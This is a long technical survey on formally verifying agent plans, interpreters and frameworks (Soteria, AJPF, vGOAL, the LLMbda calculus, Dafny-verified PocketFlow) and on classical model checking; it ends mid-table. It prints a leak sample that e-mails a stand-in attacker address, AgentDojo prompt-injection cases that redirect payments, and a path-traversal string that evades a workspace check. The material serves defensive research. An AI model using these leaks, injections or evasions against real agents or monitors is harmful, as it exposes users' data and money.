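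In the talk *Return of the Theorem*, Meijer (2026) proposes writing both plans and business rules as Horn clauses, which are rules of the form "if A and B, then C". Each set of clauses defines a table. For a car dealer, one table lists all permitted sales, and the other lists all sales the plan could make. The plan is safe if every row of its table also appears in the table of permitted sales. An SMT solver, a program that searches for values satisfying a formula, looks for a row that appears only in the plan's table. If a customer has talked the agent into selling a car for one dollar, that sale appears only in the plan's table, and the agent has to write a new plan.

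The refund limit would fit easily into this scheme because the tables contain values. A rule about the order of calls would need something extra, such as a column for time.

Meijer argues that checking a proof is easy even when finding one is hard, just as checking a completed Sudoku is easier than solving it. This is true if the model supplies the proof, as in the design described in another talk, *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls* (Meijer, 2026). But a solver that has to search for a counterexample does the hard part itself. He et al. warn that such solvers may not finish, and they limit Dafny to ten seconds per state. There are no results for Meijer's design to compare with theirs. The article acknowledges that nobody has formally measured how writing a plan first affects an agent's usefulness.

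The refund plan would need a separate version for each of these systems. Developers of BDI languages faced the same problem before AIL gave them a common layer, but these systems have no such layer. Combining the systems' strengths is also difficult. Dantas and colleagues found no approach among their 38 studies that is sound, complete and scalable, preserves the meaning of the original requirement, and leaves the agent useful.

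### Agents that decide step by step

Many agents have no complete plan to check. A programming agent looking for a bug reads an error message, opens a file and decides from its contents which file to open next. A complete plan would need a branch for everything the agent might find. The agent's graph may have only one model node and one tool node, with arrows in both directions, which allows tool calls in any order.

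A system can write a new plan whenever the agent learns something important. In conversations with customers, Soteria does this after each message. This raised the average cost of an airline task with GPT-5.4-mini from 3.1 cents for the unprotected agent to about 12.5 cents. In Toolathlon, where one plan was enough, the Opus agent cost 43 cents with Soteria and 97 cents without it, because the agent wasted fewer steps with Soteria.

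When an agent replans, the verifier can also miss a violation that spans both plans. In the proof as He and colleagues describe it, the logs are empty at the start of a plan. Suppose an agent reads a confidential file under one plan and sends an e-mail under the next, breaking the rule against sending e-mail after reading such a file. If the verifier doesn't carry the logs over, it can accept both plans. Soteria's monitor keeps the record of actual calls, so it could still block the e-mail.

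Another answer is to leave some decisions in the plan open. An `llm_eval` instruction can stand for a decision that nobody can predict, and the verifier checks the plan for every answer that the instruction's postcondition allows. This works when the possible next steps are known and only the choice between them is open. It works less well for a task such as "edit the program and test it until the tests pass", because Soteria does not allow loops. The plan would have to set a fixed number of attempts, or stop after each test so that a new plan can be generated.

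When no useful plan is possible, the software can still check each action before it takes effect. In Nguyen's *VerAct*, a language model proposes actions and a separate symbolic layer verifies them. In 28,080 trial runs with four models, the agents succeeded in 80.1% of cases and broke none of the constraints. With guardrails that relied on generated code, the success rate was only 15.4%. Using a language model as the verifier reduced performance by 41%, mainly because the model confused the order of events or made arithmetic errors.

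Checking actions one at a time cannot reveal that a permitted action will later leave the agent with no permitted way to finish its task. In their review, Dantas and colleagues rank safety over whole plans among the most important open problems. In one study they reviewed, runtime monitoring reduced household agents' unsafe actions by 65%, but its guarantees covered only single steps or short sequences. They rate the certainty of the evidence as very low for seven of the field's nine main claims, each of which rests on one or two studies.

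## What must be trusted: translator, interpreter and virtual machine

A checker rarely examines an agent in exactly the form that goes into operation. AJPF runs the delivery robot's program on JPF's virtual machine, but the robot runs it on an ordinary Java virtual machine. Soteria proves its results about a plan, but in its default mode a language model works from a flowchart of that plan. The results carry over only if the two forms match in the relevant ways. That match depends on translators, interpreters and virtual machines, which may themselves contain mistakes.

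### Faithfulness

Let C be the set of runs of the checked form and D the set of runs of the deployed agent. The checked form is faithful if every run in D is also in C. Since a property P is a set of runs too, three lines show that a verified property carries over:

```
1.  D ⊆ C     the checked form is faithful
2.  C ⊆ P     the checker has verified the property
3.  D ⊆ P     follows from 1 and 2
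```

This works for any property of single runs, whether safety or liveness. C may contain runs that the deployed agent never produces, which can cause false alarms but not missed violations.

Two runs count as the same here if they agree, state by state, on the facts the rule mentions. AJPF's formulas have no "next" operator, so it also doesn't matter if one run stays in a state for a few steps longer than the other.

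Suppose the robot's battery dies in the corridor and the checked form has no run in which this happens. D then contains a run in which the robot stays in the corridor forever, so ◇delivered fails although the checker verified it. The rule against entering an occupied corridor still holds, because everything up to the failure also happens in some checked run and the robot does nothing afterwards.

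A proof of faithfulness usually compares individual steps, because nobody can compare infinitely many runs one by one. It pairs each initial state of the deployed agent with an initial state of the checked form. It then shows that whenever the deployed agent takes a step from a paired state, the checked form can take a matching step from the other state in the pair, and the two resulting states are also paired. A relation with these properties is called a forward simulation. If the same properties also hold in the other direction, the relation is a bisimulation, and both forms have the same runs.

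### A step that the checker does not see

Suppose the delivery robot has a hatch for parcels and must never drive with the hatch open. Its program contains the two deeds `start_motor` and `close_hatch`, in that order, and its interpreter carries out both in a single reasoning cycle:

| Moment | Driving | Hatch open | Visible at the end of a cycle |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the cycle | No | Yes | Yes |
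| After `start_motor` | Yes | Yes | No |
| After `close_hatch` | Yes | No | Yes |

The robot breaks the rule in the middle row. A checker that evaluates the rule only at the end of each cycle examines just the first and last rows, so it reports no violation. It would also report none if the programmer had put the two deeds in the right order, so it can't distinguish the faulty program from the correct one. The deployed run has a state that no checked run contains, so D is not a subset of C.

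Checking the rule after every deed would reveal the open hatch. But to find a case where the porter reaches into the hatch just after the motor starts, the checker would also have to let the porter run at that point.

Merging steps is harmless if the states in between don't change any fact the rule mentions and no other agent can observe or affect them. JPF relies on this when it merges bytecode instructions. In AIL, Dennis and colleagues let the designer of each interpreter decide where in the reasoning cycle the model checker is notified of a new state. A Gwendolen agent carries out one deed per cycle, so AJPF would detect the open hatch there, but it might miss it in another language.

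### The trusted base of AJPF

The trusted base consists of all the components that must be correct for a verification result to hold of the running system. AJPF's is smaller than that of a hand-drawn model because, as *An Abstract Architecture for Explainable Autonomy in Hazardous Environments* (2026) points out, it checks the program code that the agent will run in operation. Several layers still remain:

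| Layer | What has to be right | Example of a fault |
|---|---|---|
| Parser | It turns the program's text into the right AIL data structures | It drops a condition from a plan |
| AIL interpreter | Its rules and its test for beliefs match the agent language | It ignores a failed action that the language would report |
| Environment model | It supplies every sequence of inputs that can really occur | It never presses both pedals at once |
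| AJPF controller and listener | They check at the right moments and build the right automaton | They miss the open hatch |
| JPF virtual machine | It executes bytecode correctly, tries every open choice and recognises repeated states | It mistakes a new state for an old one |
| Host Java machine and computer | They run JPF correctly | A memory error changes a stored state |
| The robot's own Java machine | It executes the program as JPF did | It switches between threads where JPF did not |

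JPF uses Jenkins hashes, which condense a state into a short number, to recognize repeated states. If two different states had the same hash and JPF compared nothing else, it would treat the second as a repeat and never explore what follows. This should be very unlikely in searches of the size reported so far, but a search that compares only hashes is not quite a proof.

A parser or interpreter fault does less damage than the table might suggest if the robot and the checker share the same parser and interpreter. A dropped condition, for example, is then missing in both places, so the search still covers what the robot will do. The fault matters when the robot runs the program on a different implementation of the language, or when it affects the test for beliefs, which AJPF uses to evaluate the specification.

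### GOAL: an interpreter without a proof

A different implementation of GOAL is a realistic possibility, since the language existed before AIL. Dennis and colleagues did not prove their interpreter equivalent to GOAL's published semantics, and they describe two gaps. First, the Java classes might not implement the rules the developers intended. The Java method for capabilities, which is more permissive than the stated rule, could be an example. Second, the rules are a variant of the published ones, for instance in how they represent capabilities. Dennis and colleagues considered a proof about the Java code outside the scope of their work. They thought that proving the two sets of rules equivalent would take manageable effort, but had not done so.

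Thirteen years later, Yang and Holvoet still listed whether AIL interprets BDI languages faithfully as a concern, but did not name an error. To prove equivalence for their own vGOAL translator, they defined a bisimulation that also requires paired states to have the same labels.

The translator generates the model using the same implementation of vGOAL's decision-making as the vGOAL interpreter. This makes it likely that the model and the running program agree, but any mistake in that code would affect both. The proof concerns the algorithm on paper, which can differ from the program. In the printed version, the loop that should find the final states goes through a set that the previous line has emptied, so it would never find any. This is very probably a misprint that isn't in the code, but the proof can't establish that.

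### Proving the interpreter itself: the LLMbda calculus

One can prove a theorem about the interpreter once, for all programs it can run, instead of proving each translation correct. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) does this for the LLMbda calculus, a small language that can express agents such as CaMeL.

They motivate it with mistakes in CaMeL's interpreter, which is supposed to stop secret data from reaching outsiders. One of the leaks has roughly this form:

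```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                          rich = False
if rich:                         send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

For a customer with a high balance, the third line sets `tmp` to False, and CaMeL labels `tmp` secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` keeps its public label and CaMeL allows the e-mail. For a customer with a low balance, no e-mail goes out, so the attacker learns whether the balance is high or low. Garby and colleagues also found that inserting an untrusted value into a piece of text made the value trusted. In both cases, the security policy was fine, but the interpreter applied it incorrectly.

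The LLMbda calculus extends the lambda calculus, a minimal programming language built from functions. The program's state is a conversation with a language model, and every value has a label. In the examples, a label can contain U for "untrusted", S for "secret", both or neither. The main additions are:

| Expression | Effect |
|---|---|
| `@e` | Sends `e` to the model, parses the answer as code and runs it |
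| `fork e` | Evaluates `e` in a copy of the conversation, then discards the copy |
| `clear` | Empties the conversation |
| `l : e` | Adds the label `l` to the value of `e` |
| `l ? e` | Tests whether the label of `e` stays within `l` |
| `assert l e` | Stops the program unless it does |
| `endorse l e` | Changes the label of `e` from untrusted to trusted |

A program can build a quarantined model from these parts. It forks the conversation, clears the copy and lets the model read an untrusted e-mail there, so the e-mail never enters the main conversation. The interpreter also keeps a label for the current position in the program. If the program branches on a secret, everything inside the branch counts as secret, and the interpreter blocks the branch from adding anything to a public conversation. This prevents a leak like the one in CaMeL.

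### Noninterference

The central theorem is noninterference, which means that untrusted input can't change what an observer of only trusted data sees, and secrets can't change what an observer of only public data sees. If the language model always gave the same answer to the same conversation, the theorem would be that when two inputs look the same to the observer and both runs finish, their results also look the same.

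Real models answer at random, so the theorem has to compare probabilities. Suppose that an attacker can choose between inputs A and B, and that the observer sees "yes", "no" or no result at all:

| | "Yes" | "No" | No result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input A | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| Input B | 0.4 | 0.5 | 0.1 |
| Common upper bound | 0.5 | 0.5 | 0 |

The theorem guarantees a common upper bound whose probabilities add up to at most 1. The two inputs could then differ only in how often they prevent a result. If input B led to "no" with probability 0.6, the bound would add up to 1.1, so no LLMbda program could behave like this. When both inputs always lead to a result, the two rows must be identical. In general, the statistical distance between them is at most the average probability of no result, which is 0.15 in the example.

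"No result" includes runs that the interpreter stops because of a policy. An attacker may therefore still be able to make an agent fail.

To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs. It skips any computation as soon as its label hides it from the observer, and continues with an empty value. This version can't depend on anything hidden, so it produces exactly the same distribution for inputs A and B. It also produces each visible result at least as often as the normal version does, so its distribution is the common upper bound.

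The proofs and the interpreter are both written in Lean. The interpreter is an ordinary function whose inputs include an "oracle", a table with the model's answer to every possible conversation at every call. A further theorem states that running the interpreter with a randomly drawn table gives results with exactly the probabilities that the language's definition prescribes. In live use, requests to the model's provider replace the table.

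The trusted base still includes Lean and the code that sends the request. The proof also assumes that each of the model's answers is drawn independently and depends only on the conversation. If a provider's model retained information from other conversations, this assumption would be false, and a secret could leak through the retained information.

### Endorsement and what an agent inherits

Strict noninterference would make many agents useless, because they have to act on untrusted data such as e-mails. With `endorse`, a program can declare such data trusted. If the endorsed value can only be one of eight fixed categories, an attacker can influence at most three bits. But if the program endorses an account number from a file, the attacker may be able to choose where a payment goes.

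Garby and colleagues prove that endorsement weakens only the protection against untrusted data. Secrets stay equally well protected however a program uses `endorse`. Endorsement also has no effect in code that the model generated from untrusted data, because the interpreter treats everything in that code as untrusted. This safeguard fails if the program endorsed the data before the model read it.

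These guarantees hold for every agent written in the calculus without a separate proof, even if the model writes part of the agent's code during the run. They do not limit refunds. Noninterference does not restrict a refund of 5,000 that the user requested, because it involves no untrusted data. The developer also has to label the data sources correctly and put an `assert` in front of every sensitive tool.

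Garby and colleagues tested the agent Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Randori first tries its plan in an artificial bank, so that error messages caused by real data can't influence the next attempt. Across three models, it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. Two thirds of the task-attack combinations are easy to resist, because the attack needs a tool call that a plan for the task would never contain. The 423 harder attempts are more informative, and two of them succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill according to a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.

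Endorsement made those two attacks possible, but it also made the agent more useful. When no attack took place, Randori with Qwen3.7-plus completed 75% of the tasks with endorsement and 62.5% without it. CaMeL, tested with two other models, completed 37.5% with its policies switched on. There were only 16 different tasks, so each figure is uncertain by around 20 percentage points. The tools were simulated inside the calculus, and Garby and colleagues name the connection to real external tools as a limitation.

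### A verified agent framework

Most developers will not rewrite their agents in a new calculus. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) instead uses Dafny to verify the framework around the model. The framework is PocketFlow, which is very small and represents an agent as a graph of steps. The model chooses an action, and a loop in the framework carries it out and moves to the next step.

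In the proof, the model is a procedure without a body. Dafny therefore has to assume that it may return any action that the interface permits, as if an adversary had chosen it. The proved property has three parts:

- The path of every file that the agent reads starts with the name of the workspace folder.
- Every tool that the agent calls is on a list of allowed tools.
- The number of steps never exceeds a limit.

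Moon and Varshney first prove that an abstract description of the framework has this property. They then use a forward simulation to show that a more detailed description takes only steps the abstract one allows. If the model requests a forbidden action, both descriptions record that nothing happened. Dafny's compiler turns the verified code into Python. The guarantee applies to this Python program and does not automatically extend to the original PocketFlow.

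The first part of the property may be weaker than it looks. If the workspace is `/work`, the path `/work/../private/key` starts with `/work` but leads to a file outside the workspace. A plain text comparison would accept this path, so the framework needs to resolve paths before checking them. The second part, like any list of allowed tools, does not restrict how the agent uses those tools. If the list includes a general command line, the agent can do almost anything.

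Language models did most of the proof work. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the specification and the proof and repaired failed attempts. Each of the four runs on two example agents used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens. Dafny then took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through the graph. Moon and Varshney give no figure for the human work on the fixed parts of the proof.

A model that writes both a specification and its proof may produce a specification that every program satisfies. Moon and Varshney guard against this mainly by hiding the framework's code from the model while it writes the safety property. They also damage each proof in two ways and require Dafny to reject both versions.

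These safeguards did not catch everything. The second example agent reads documents from a permitted list, but the fixed template had a field for tool calls and none for documents. When the model was not shown the code, it recorded each document as a tool call, so the rule about permitted tools covered the documents. When it was shown the code, it left the field empty. With no tool calls recorded, the rule "every recorded tool call is on the list" was trivially true, so Dafny accepted the proof even though nothing had checked the documents.

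The guarantee also depends on what Moon and Varshney call effect exclusivity, meaning that the agent can affect the outside world only through the verified loop. A Python library that opens its own network connection would break this assumption. The trusted base also includes the policy, Dafny and its compiler, and the code that turns the model's text into an action. Moon and Varshney recommend running the framework in a sandbox to limit the damage if one of these fails. The language model is not part of the trusted base, so replacing it with a more capable one does not invalidate the proof.

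### Properties that compare runs

The three-line proof of faithfulness covers properties that each run has or lacks on its own. Noninterference is a relation between runs, so it needs a separate argument.

Some properties concern all pairs of runs, for example "any two runs open the same public web page, whatever the patient's diagnosis". If such a property holds for every pair of runs in C, the checked agent's runs, it also holds for every pair in D, the deployed agent's runs, because every pair from D is also a pair from C.

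Other properties require a matching run to exist. Suppose an agent reads a diagnosis and then opens page A or page B. Its program leaves the choice of page open, but the interpreter on the deployed agent always makes the choice in the same way:

| Diagnosis | Page | Run of the checked program | Run of the deployed agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flu | A | Yes | Yes |
| Flu | B | Yes | No |
| Asthma | A | Yes | No |
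| Asthma | B | Yes | Yes |

The privacy rule requires that every run have a counterpart with the other diagnosis and the same page. The checked program satisfies this rule, since someone who sees page A can't tell which diagnosis the patient has. The deployed agent has only two of the four runs. It is faithful by the definition above and keeps every property of single runs, but the page now reveals the diagnosis. GOAL programs could have this problem, because each interpreter chooses between applicable actions in its own way.

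A bisimulation avoids the problem because it also requires the deployed agent to have every run of the checked program, including those the rule needs. When answers are random, having the same runs is not enough. If the checked program opened each page half the time and the deployed agent opened page A in 99% of flu cases and 1% of asthma cases, all four runs would still exist, but the choice of page would almost reveal the diagnosis. It therefore matters that the theorem about the LLMbda interpreter establishes equal probabilities, and not just that every result of the interpreter is permitted.

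## Comparison with other formal methods for reactive and multi-agent systems

A reactive system keeps responding to its surroundings, unlike an ordinary calculation, which produces a result and stops. Lift controllers, robots and agents that serve one customer after another are reactive systems. Most formal methods for these systems don't run the agent's program on a virtual machine. The methods need different inputs and are used to answer different questions, so applying them to a single example makes them easier to compare.

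Robots A and B work at opposite ends of a corridor that has room for only one of them. At any moment, each robot is away, waiting at its door or inside the corridor. The engineers have two requirements:

```
safety:    □ ¬(insideA ∧ insideB)
progress:  □ (waitingA → ◇insideA)  ∧  □ (waitingB → ◇insideB)
```

AJPF would need both robots' programs and a Java model of the corridor. It could establish whether these two programs meet the requirements, but not how likely a collision is if a sensor is unreliable, or what happens when a third robot arrives.

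### Models written by hand

To use Spin or NuSMV, an engineer describes the robots' behaviour in the checker's own language. Suppose each robot must take a lock before entering the corridor and release it after leaving. Each robot can be in three situations, which makes nine combinations. The lock rules out the one with both robots inside, so the checker visits eight states and the safety rule holds. Progress fails because robot A can keep leaving, returning and retaking the lock indefinitely while robot B waits. A lock that lets the robots take turns when both are waiting would solve this, provided that every robot eventually leaves the corridor.

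NuSMV also accepts formulas in computation tree logic (CTL), which can state that something happens on some run or on every run. The CTL formula AG EF (awayA ∧ awayB) means that from every reachable state, both robots can get back to where they started. LTL cannot express this property, because an LTL formula describes each run separately, whereas this property depends on which runs are possible from each state. AJPF's property language therefore can't express it either.

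Hand-written models can be very large, since modern checkers can handle hundreds of millions of states, as Yang and Holvoet (2025) note in *Efficient Model Checking with Semantically-Equivalent Models for vGOAL*. But the check covers only the lock as the engineer described it. If robot B's program releases the lock when the robot reaches the exit, instead of after it has passed through, the check won't reveal that the model is wrong.

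The method also works for the software around a language model. *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies in Multi-Agent Large Language Model Systems* (2026) describes AgentVerify, which represents this software as a finite-state machine and treats the language model as an oracle that may return any output. If language models controlled the robots, such a check could show that the lock prevents collisions whatever the models output. It could not prove progress without further assumptions, because a model might never output a request to leave the corridor.

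### Deriving a controller from the specification

Reactive synthesis needs no program. The engineer supplies the specification and states which facts the environment determines and which the controller determines. In the example, the environment determines who is waiting and whether the corridor is free, and the controller gives permission to enter. The synthesis tool treats this as a game in which the environment moves, the controller responds, and the controller wins if the resulting infinite run satisfies the specification.

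For a safety rule, the tool starts with every state that doesn't break the rule. It then removes each state from which the environment can force the game out of the remaining set, and repeats this until nothing changes. If the initial state is still in the set, a controller can satisfy the rule by always choosing a move that stays in the set. Otherwise, no controller can satisfy the rule, which is useful to know before writing one.

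Pnueli and Rosner proved in 1989 that synthesis from full LTL is complete for doubly exponential time. For a formula of length n, the time can grow roughly like 2 to the power of 2ⁿ, which is about 65,000 for n = 4 and about 18 billion billion for n = 6. Model checking takes much less computation, since its running time grows in proportion to the size of the model, although it can also grow exponentially with the length of the formula.

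Many practical specifications fit into a simpler fragment called GR(1), short for "generalized reactivity of rank 1". It allows conditions on the initial state, rules about single steps, and one implication about things that happen again and again. For the corridor, the rules about single steps are that the controller never gives both robots permission and gives permission only when the corridor is free. The implication is

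```
□◇free  →  □◇(¬waitingA ∨ permitA)  ∧  □◇(¬waitingB ∨ permitB)
```

The left side is the assumption that the corridor keeps becoming free. The right side means that each waiting robot eventually receives permission, provided it keeps waiting until then. A controller that remembers which robot went last can satisfy this. Piterman, Pnueli and Sa'ar showed in 2006 that GR(1) synthesis takes time proportional to about N³, where N is the number of states. This is manageable for small controllers, but N doubles with every additional yes-or-no fact.

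A synthesised controller satisfies the formula, sometimes in ways the engineer did not intend. If the controller also operates the exit doors, it could lock robot A in the corridor, which would then never become free again. This would make the assumption false and the implication true, but robot B would wait forever.

The example also has one central controller that knows about both robots. If each robot has to decide from its own observations, the engineer needs two programs that work together. Pnueli and Rosner showed in 1990 that no algorithm can solve this distributed version in general.

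Synthesis could produce the gatekeeper that decides which of a language model's requests to allow, but it can't produce an agent that understands customers' complaints, because nobody can write a complete specification of that task.

### What agents know and what they can bring about

MCMAS is a model checker for multi-agent systems that can check CTL formulas and formulas about agents' knowledge and strategic abilities. Its input is a hand-written model that gives each agent a local state, which consists of what that agent can observe and remember. An agent knows a fact if the fact is true in every reachable situation where the agent has the same local state.

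Suppose that robot A can't see into the corridor but can see a lamp, which should be on when the corridor is occupied:

| Situation | What robot A sees | Robot B inside |
|---|---|---|
| Corridor free | Lamp off | No |
| Corridor occupied | Lamp on | Yes |
| Corridor occupied, bulb broken | Lamp off | Yes |

If bulbs never break, only the first two situations are possible, and robot A knows that the corridor is free when the lamp is off. If the model includes broken bulbs, robot A no longer knows this, because two situations look the same to it and robot B is inside in one of them. MCMAS would therefore reject the rule "robot A enters only if it knows the corridor is free". AJPF could accept the rule "robot A enters only if it believes the corridor is free" in both cases, because it only checks whether robot A holds that belief.

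MCMAS can also nest these operators, as in "robot A knows that robot B knows that the corridor is closed". AJPF's grammar does not allow such nesting. Anything an agent knows in MCMAS is true, while a BDI agent's beliefs can be wrong, so similar-looking formulas in the two tools express different properties.

Alternating-time temporal logic (ATL) describes what a group of agents can achieve, whatever the others do. Three formulas for the corridor show the idea:

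```
⟨⟨A⟩⟩ ◇crossedA                  A can make sure that it crosses
⟨⟨A,B⟩⟩ ◇(crossedA ∧ crossedB)   together, they can make sure that both cross
⟨⟨B⟩⟩ □¬crossedA                 B can keep A out forever
```

If robot B can stay in the corridor indefinitely, the second and third formulas are true and the first is false. These results depend on the actions available to the robots, not on their current programs. Robot B's current program might never block the corridor, but the third formula would still be true because a replacement program could.

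A strategy should only use information that the agent has. Otherwise, robot A could "choose" to enter exactly when the corridor is free without being able to see whether it is. This requirement makes ATL much harder to check. Dantas and colleagues cite a 2011 proof that the problem is undecidable for agents that have incomplete information and remember everything they observe. Practical tools therefore have to restrict the agents' memory or information.

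According to *Do LLM Agents Negotiate Rationally?* (2026), ATL*, a more expressive version of ATL, remains the dominant specification language for multi-agent verification tools. The paper reports no earlier work that used such verification to check whether language-model agents follow a negotiation protocol. Its software checks individual messages while the agents negotiate, because full model checking would be less practical in a live system. Strategic logic could still be useful for these agents. For example, it could be used to check whether an attacker who controls one agent can force a data leak with that agent's tools, and the answer would not depend on how the language model normally behaves.

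### Probabilities and the LISA architecture

PRISM calculates how likely an event is, and it needs probabilities as input. Suppose robot B is in the corridor 20% of the time when robot A arrives, and robot A's sensor misses it 5% of the time. The robots then collide in 1% of crossings. If the crossings are independent, the chance of at least one collision in 100 crossings is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%.

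The assumption of independence matters greatly here. If 5% of sensors are permanently broken and the others always work, the chance of a collision in one crossing is still 1%. But the chance of at least one collision in 100 crossings is only about 5%, because a robot with a working sensor never collides. PRISM would calculate the correct figure for either model, but the engineer has to know which model fits the sensor.

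AJPF can export its models to PRISM but has to build them first. Izzo, Qu and Veres (2016), in *Reducing complexity of autonomous control agents for verifiability*, instead simplified the agent itself. Their Limited Instruction Set Agent (LISA) is based on Jason. A Jason agent handles one event and carries out one action in each reasoning cycle, so a model has to keep track of pending events and actions. A LISA agent handles all current events and carries out the next action of every active plan. It also treats goals as beliefs. This reduces the number of states, but a specification can no longer distinguish goals from beliefs the way an AJPF formula can.

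*A stochastically verifiable autonomous control architecture with reasoning* (Izzo, Qu and Veres, 2018) describes the later version, which compiles an agent automatically into a PRISM model. The programmer writes the agent in sEnglish, a restricted form of English, and adds probabilities for its surroundings. For each action, the programmer also specifies the probability that a report of the result arrives and the average number of reasoning cycles this takes. A state consists of the agent's current beliefs, the latest events and its position in each plan. Even ten possible beliefs give about a million combinations of beliefs and events, although an agent may never reach most of them.

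In 2016, Izzo and colleagues argued that every LISA agent corresponds to a Markov chain. The 2018 paper limits this claim to agents in which no two plans have the same triggering condition. Other agents need a Markov decision process, which also contains choices with no assigned probabilities. PRISM can then calculate the lowest and highest probability of an event across all the ways the agent could make these choices.

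The printed condition for a Markov chain still seems too weak. A triggering condition consists of an event and a requirement on the agent's beliefs. Suppose one plan applies when the corridor becomes free and the battery is full, and another when the corridor becomes free and a parcel is waiting. These triggering conditions are different, but both can be true at once, so the agent has a choice. The proof needs triggering conditions that can't overlap.

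Izzo and colleagues also use the model while the agent is running. If several plans apply, the agent can use PRISM to predict their likely consequences before it chooses. Izzo and colleagues consider most earlier methods too slow for this and describe JPF and AJPF as a significant bottleneck. LISA avoids the bottleneck by generating the PRISM model directly from the agent program. The result then depends on the compiler and on probabilities that the programmer has to measure or estimate.

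### Any number of robots

Checking a system with two robots doesn't show that it is safe with three, and checking larger systems one at a time can never cover every possible number of robots. In 1986, Apt and Kozen proved that no algorithm can decide in general whether a rule holds for systems of every size. Some useful special cases are decidable, especially when all agents run the same program.

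One technique counts the agents in each situation instead of tracking them individually, and treats all counts above a limit as equal. For the corridor with a lock, it is enough to record whether the lock is free and whether zero, one, or at least two robots are inside:

| Lock | Robots inside | Possible next step |
|---|---|---|
| Free | 0 | A robot takes the lock and enters |
| Taken | 1 | The robot leaves and releases the lock |

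The search finds only these two states. It never reaches "at least two robots inside", so the safety rule holds for any number of robots. But the count does not record which robot is inside, so this model can't show whether a particular robot waits forever. The model would also have to change if some robots had priority over others.

Another technique uses a cutoff, a number k such that a property holds for every number of agents if it holds for systems of up to k agents. In 1995, Emerson and Namjoshi proved small cutoffs for certain properties of rings of identical processes that pass a token around. Kouvaros and Lomuscio later developed cutoff methods for multi-agent systems and properties about what agents know. Someone has to prove that a cutoff exists for each class of system before engineers can check a few agents and draw conclusions about larger numbers.

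Swarm languages make it easier to describe many agents but don't necessarily solve this problem. In LAbS, a language by De Nicola, Di Stefano and Inverso, a programmer describes how each type of agent behaves and how many agents of each type there are. The tool SLiVER can translate this description into a C program, which repeatedly picks an agent and carries out one of its steps. An existing verifier for C then looks for violations. C serves as the intermediate language, so LAbS benefits from any improvement to the verifier. But each check covers only a fixed number of agents. A bounded verifier also examines only a limited number of steps, so it may miss a collision that happens later.

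Buzz, another swarm language, compiles to bytecode for its own virtual machine. That machine runs on the robots and executes a single run of the program, so it has a different purpose from JPF's virtual machine, which searches all possible runs.

### vGOAL and the case for AJPF

Yang and Holvoet developed their translation of vGOAL programs partly in response to AJPF. Their main criticisms are that AJPF is slow and searches the program again for every property, and that the comparison of AJPF with Spin and PRISM used simple examples, the largest with 408 states. They also question whether AIL interprets BDI languages faithfully.

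The objection about speed is justified, but exporting the model already avoids the repeated searches. The figure of 408 states is for the PRISM examples only. AJPF searched 16,609 states in the largest satellite example, at about 3.5 states per second. vGOAL's translator generated about 20 states per second in its smallest three-robot case and fewer than two in its largest. The programs, computers and definitions of a state are all different, so the published times don't show which tool is faster, let alone that vGOAL has a large advantage.

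The closest thing to a direct measurement, summarised by Yang and Holvoet, is Jongmans and colleagues' comparison of three checkers on a single GOAL agent that rearranges blocks. A checker built directly around the GOAL interpreter was faster than both AJPF and a checker based on Maude, so running the agent's own interpreter doesn't have to be as slow as it is in AJPF. But the fastest checker handled only one agent and had no techniques for reducing the number of states.

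Yang and Holvoet have since made their translator faster. The 2025 version stores transitions it has already calculated, so its running time still depends on the number of states but no longer on the number of goals. They tested it in 30 scenarios, but only against their own earlier version.

Some of the formulas in the 2024 warehouse study also don't match their descriptions. One should state that the robots can finish on a run without errors. The printed version is

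```
EG (no_error → EF finished)
```

This can be true even if every way to finish goes through an error, because "EF finished" doesn't exclude errors along the way. The printed safety rules cover each robot's battery level and location. They don't forbid two robots from sharing a location, although the robots have to ask for permission to move so that they don't collide.

The best argument for AJPF comes from a problem in vGOAL. *Bridging the Semantic Gap in vGOAL for Verifiable Autonomous Decision-Making* (Yang and Holvoet, 2025) reports that vGOAL's interpreter and checker defined the next state differently. The interpreter made new decisions as soon as one robot had finished its action, while the checker waited for all of them. In one example, two robots travel to the same location by different routes. The location goes to the first robot that asks for it, and Robot 1 has priority if both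 ask at once. In the checker, both robots always arrived together, so Robot 1 always went first. On the real robots, Robot 2 could arrive earlier and go first, so the checker would have passed a rule that Robot 2 never goes before Robot 1 even though the real robots could break it.

The earlier equivalence proof had not revealed this difference. AJPF would normally explore both orders, because its controller tries each agent as the next to run. Yang and Holvoet acknowledge that interpreter-based methods generally match the running program better.

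They changed the interpreter to match the checker, so robots that finish early now wait for the others. Changing the checker instead would have increased the number of states exponentially. To shorten the waits, they divided long journeys into short moves. In their longest run, this reduced the time spent moving from 26 to 17 units. The number of states rose from 1,186 to 2,635, and checking time rose from 41 to 219 seconds. Both versions of the program used the interpreter that waits, so the experiment doesn't measure how much time the robots lose compared with the original interpreter.

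Dennis and colleagues accept AJPF's slowness because nobody has to write a separate model and because a certification authority receives evidence about the program that the company will use. They compare choosing an AIL interpreter over a language's standard one to choosing between two C compilers. This comparison somewhat favours AIL, because the AIL interpreter for GOAL has not been proved equivalent to the standard one. They admit that the standard interpreters are often more efficient and easier to use, but a company that checks its agent with AIL and then runs it on the standard interpreter loses the main benefit of the method.

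### A language model as a policy

The methods so far treat a language model as a source of arbitrary answers, if they can include one at all. Gross, Spieker and Gotlieb (2025), in *Verifying Memoryless Sequential Decision-making of Large Language Models*, check the answers themselves. Their tool needs a Markov decision process that describes the task, a safety property, a way to turn each state into a prompt, and a way to turn the model's answer into an action. It then builds a Markov chain:

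1. It describes the current state in a prompt and asks the language model for an action.
2. It adds every state to which that action can lead, with the corresponding probabilities.
3. It repeats this for each new state until there are none left.
4. It passes the result to the probabilistic checker Storm.

For robot A in the corridor example, there are only nine combinations of positions, so nine prompts would be enough. The tool ignores states that the language model's choices never lead to, which can make the Markov chain much smaller than the full task.

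Gross and colleagues tested five small open models on three tasks. A taxi should not run out of fuel, an agent on a frozen lake should not slip into the water, and a trader should not go bankrupt. The table gives the probability of each accident, with a policy trained by reinforcement learning for comparison:

| Model | Taxi | Frozen lake | Stock market |
|---|---|---|---|
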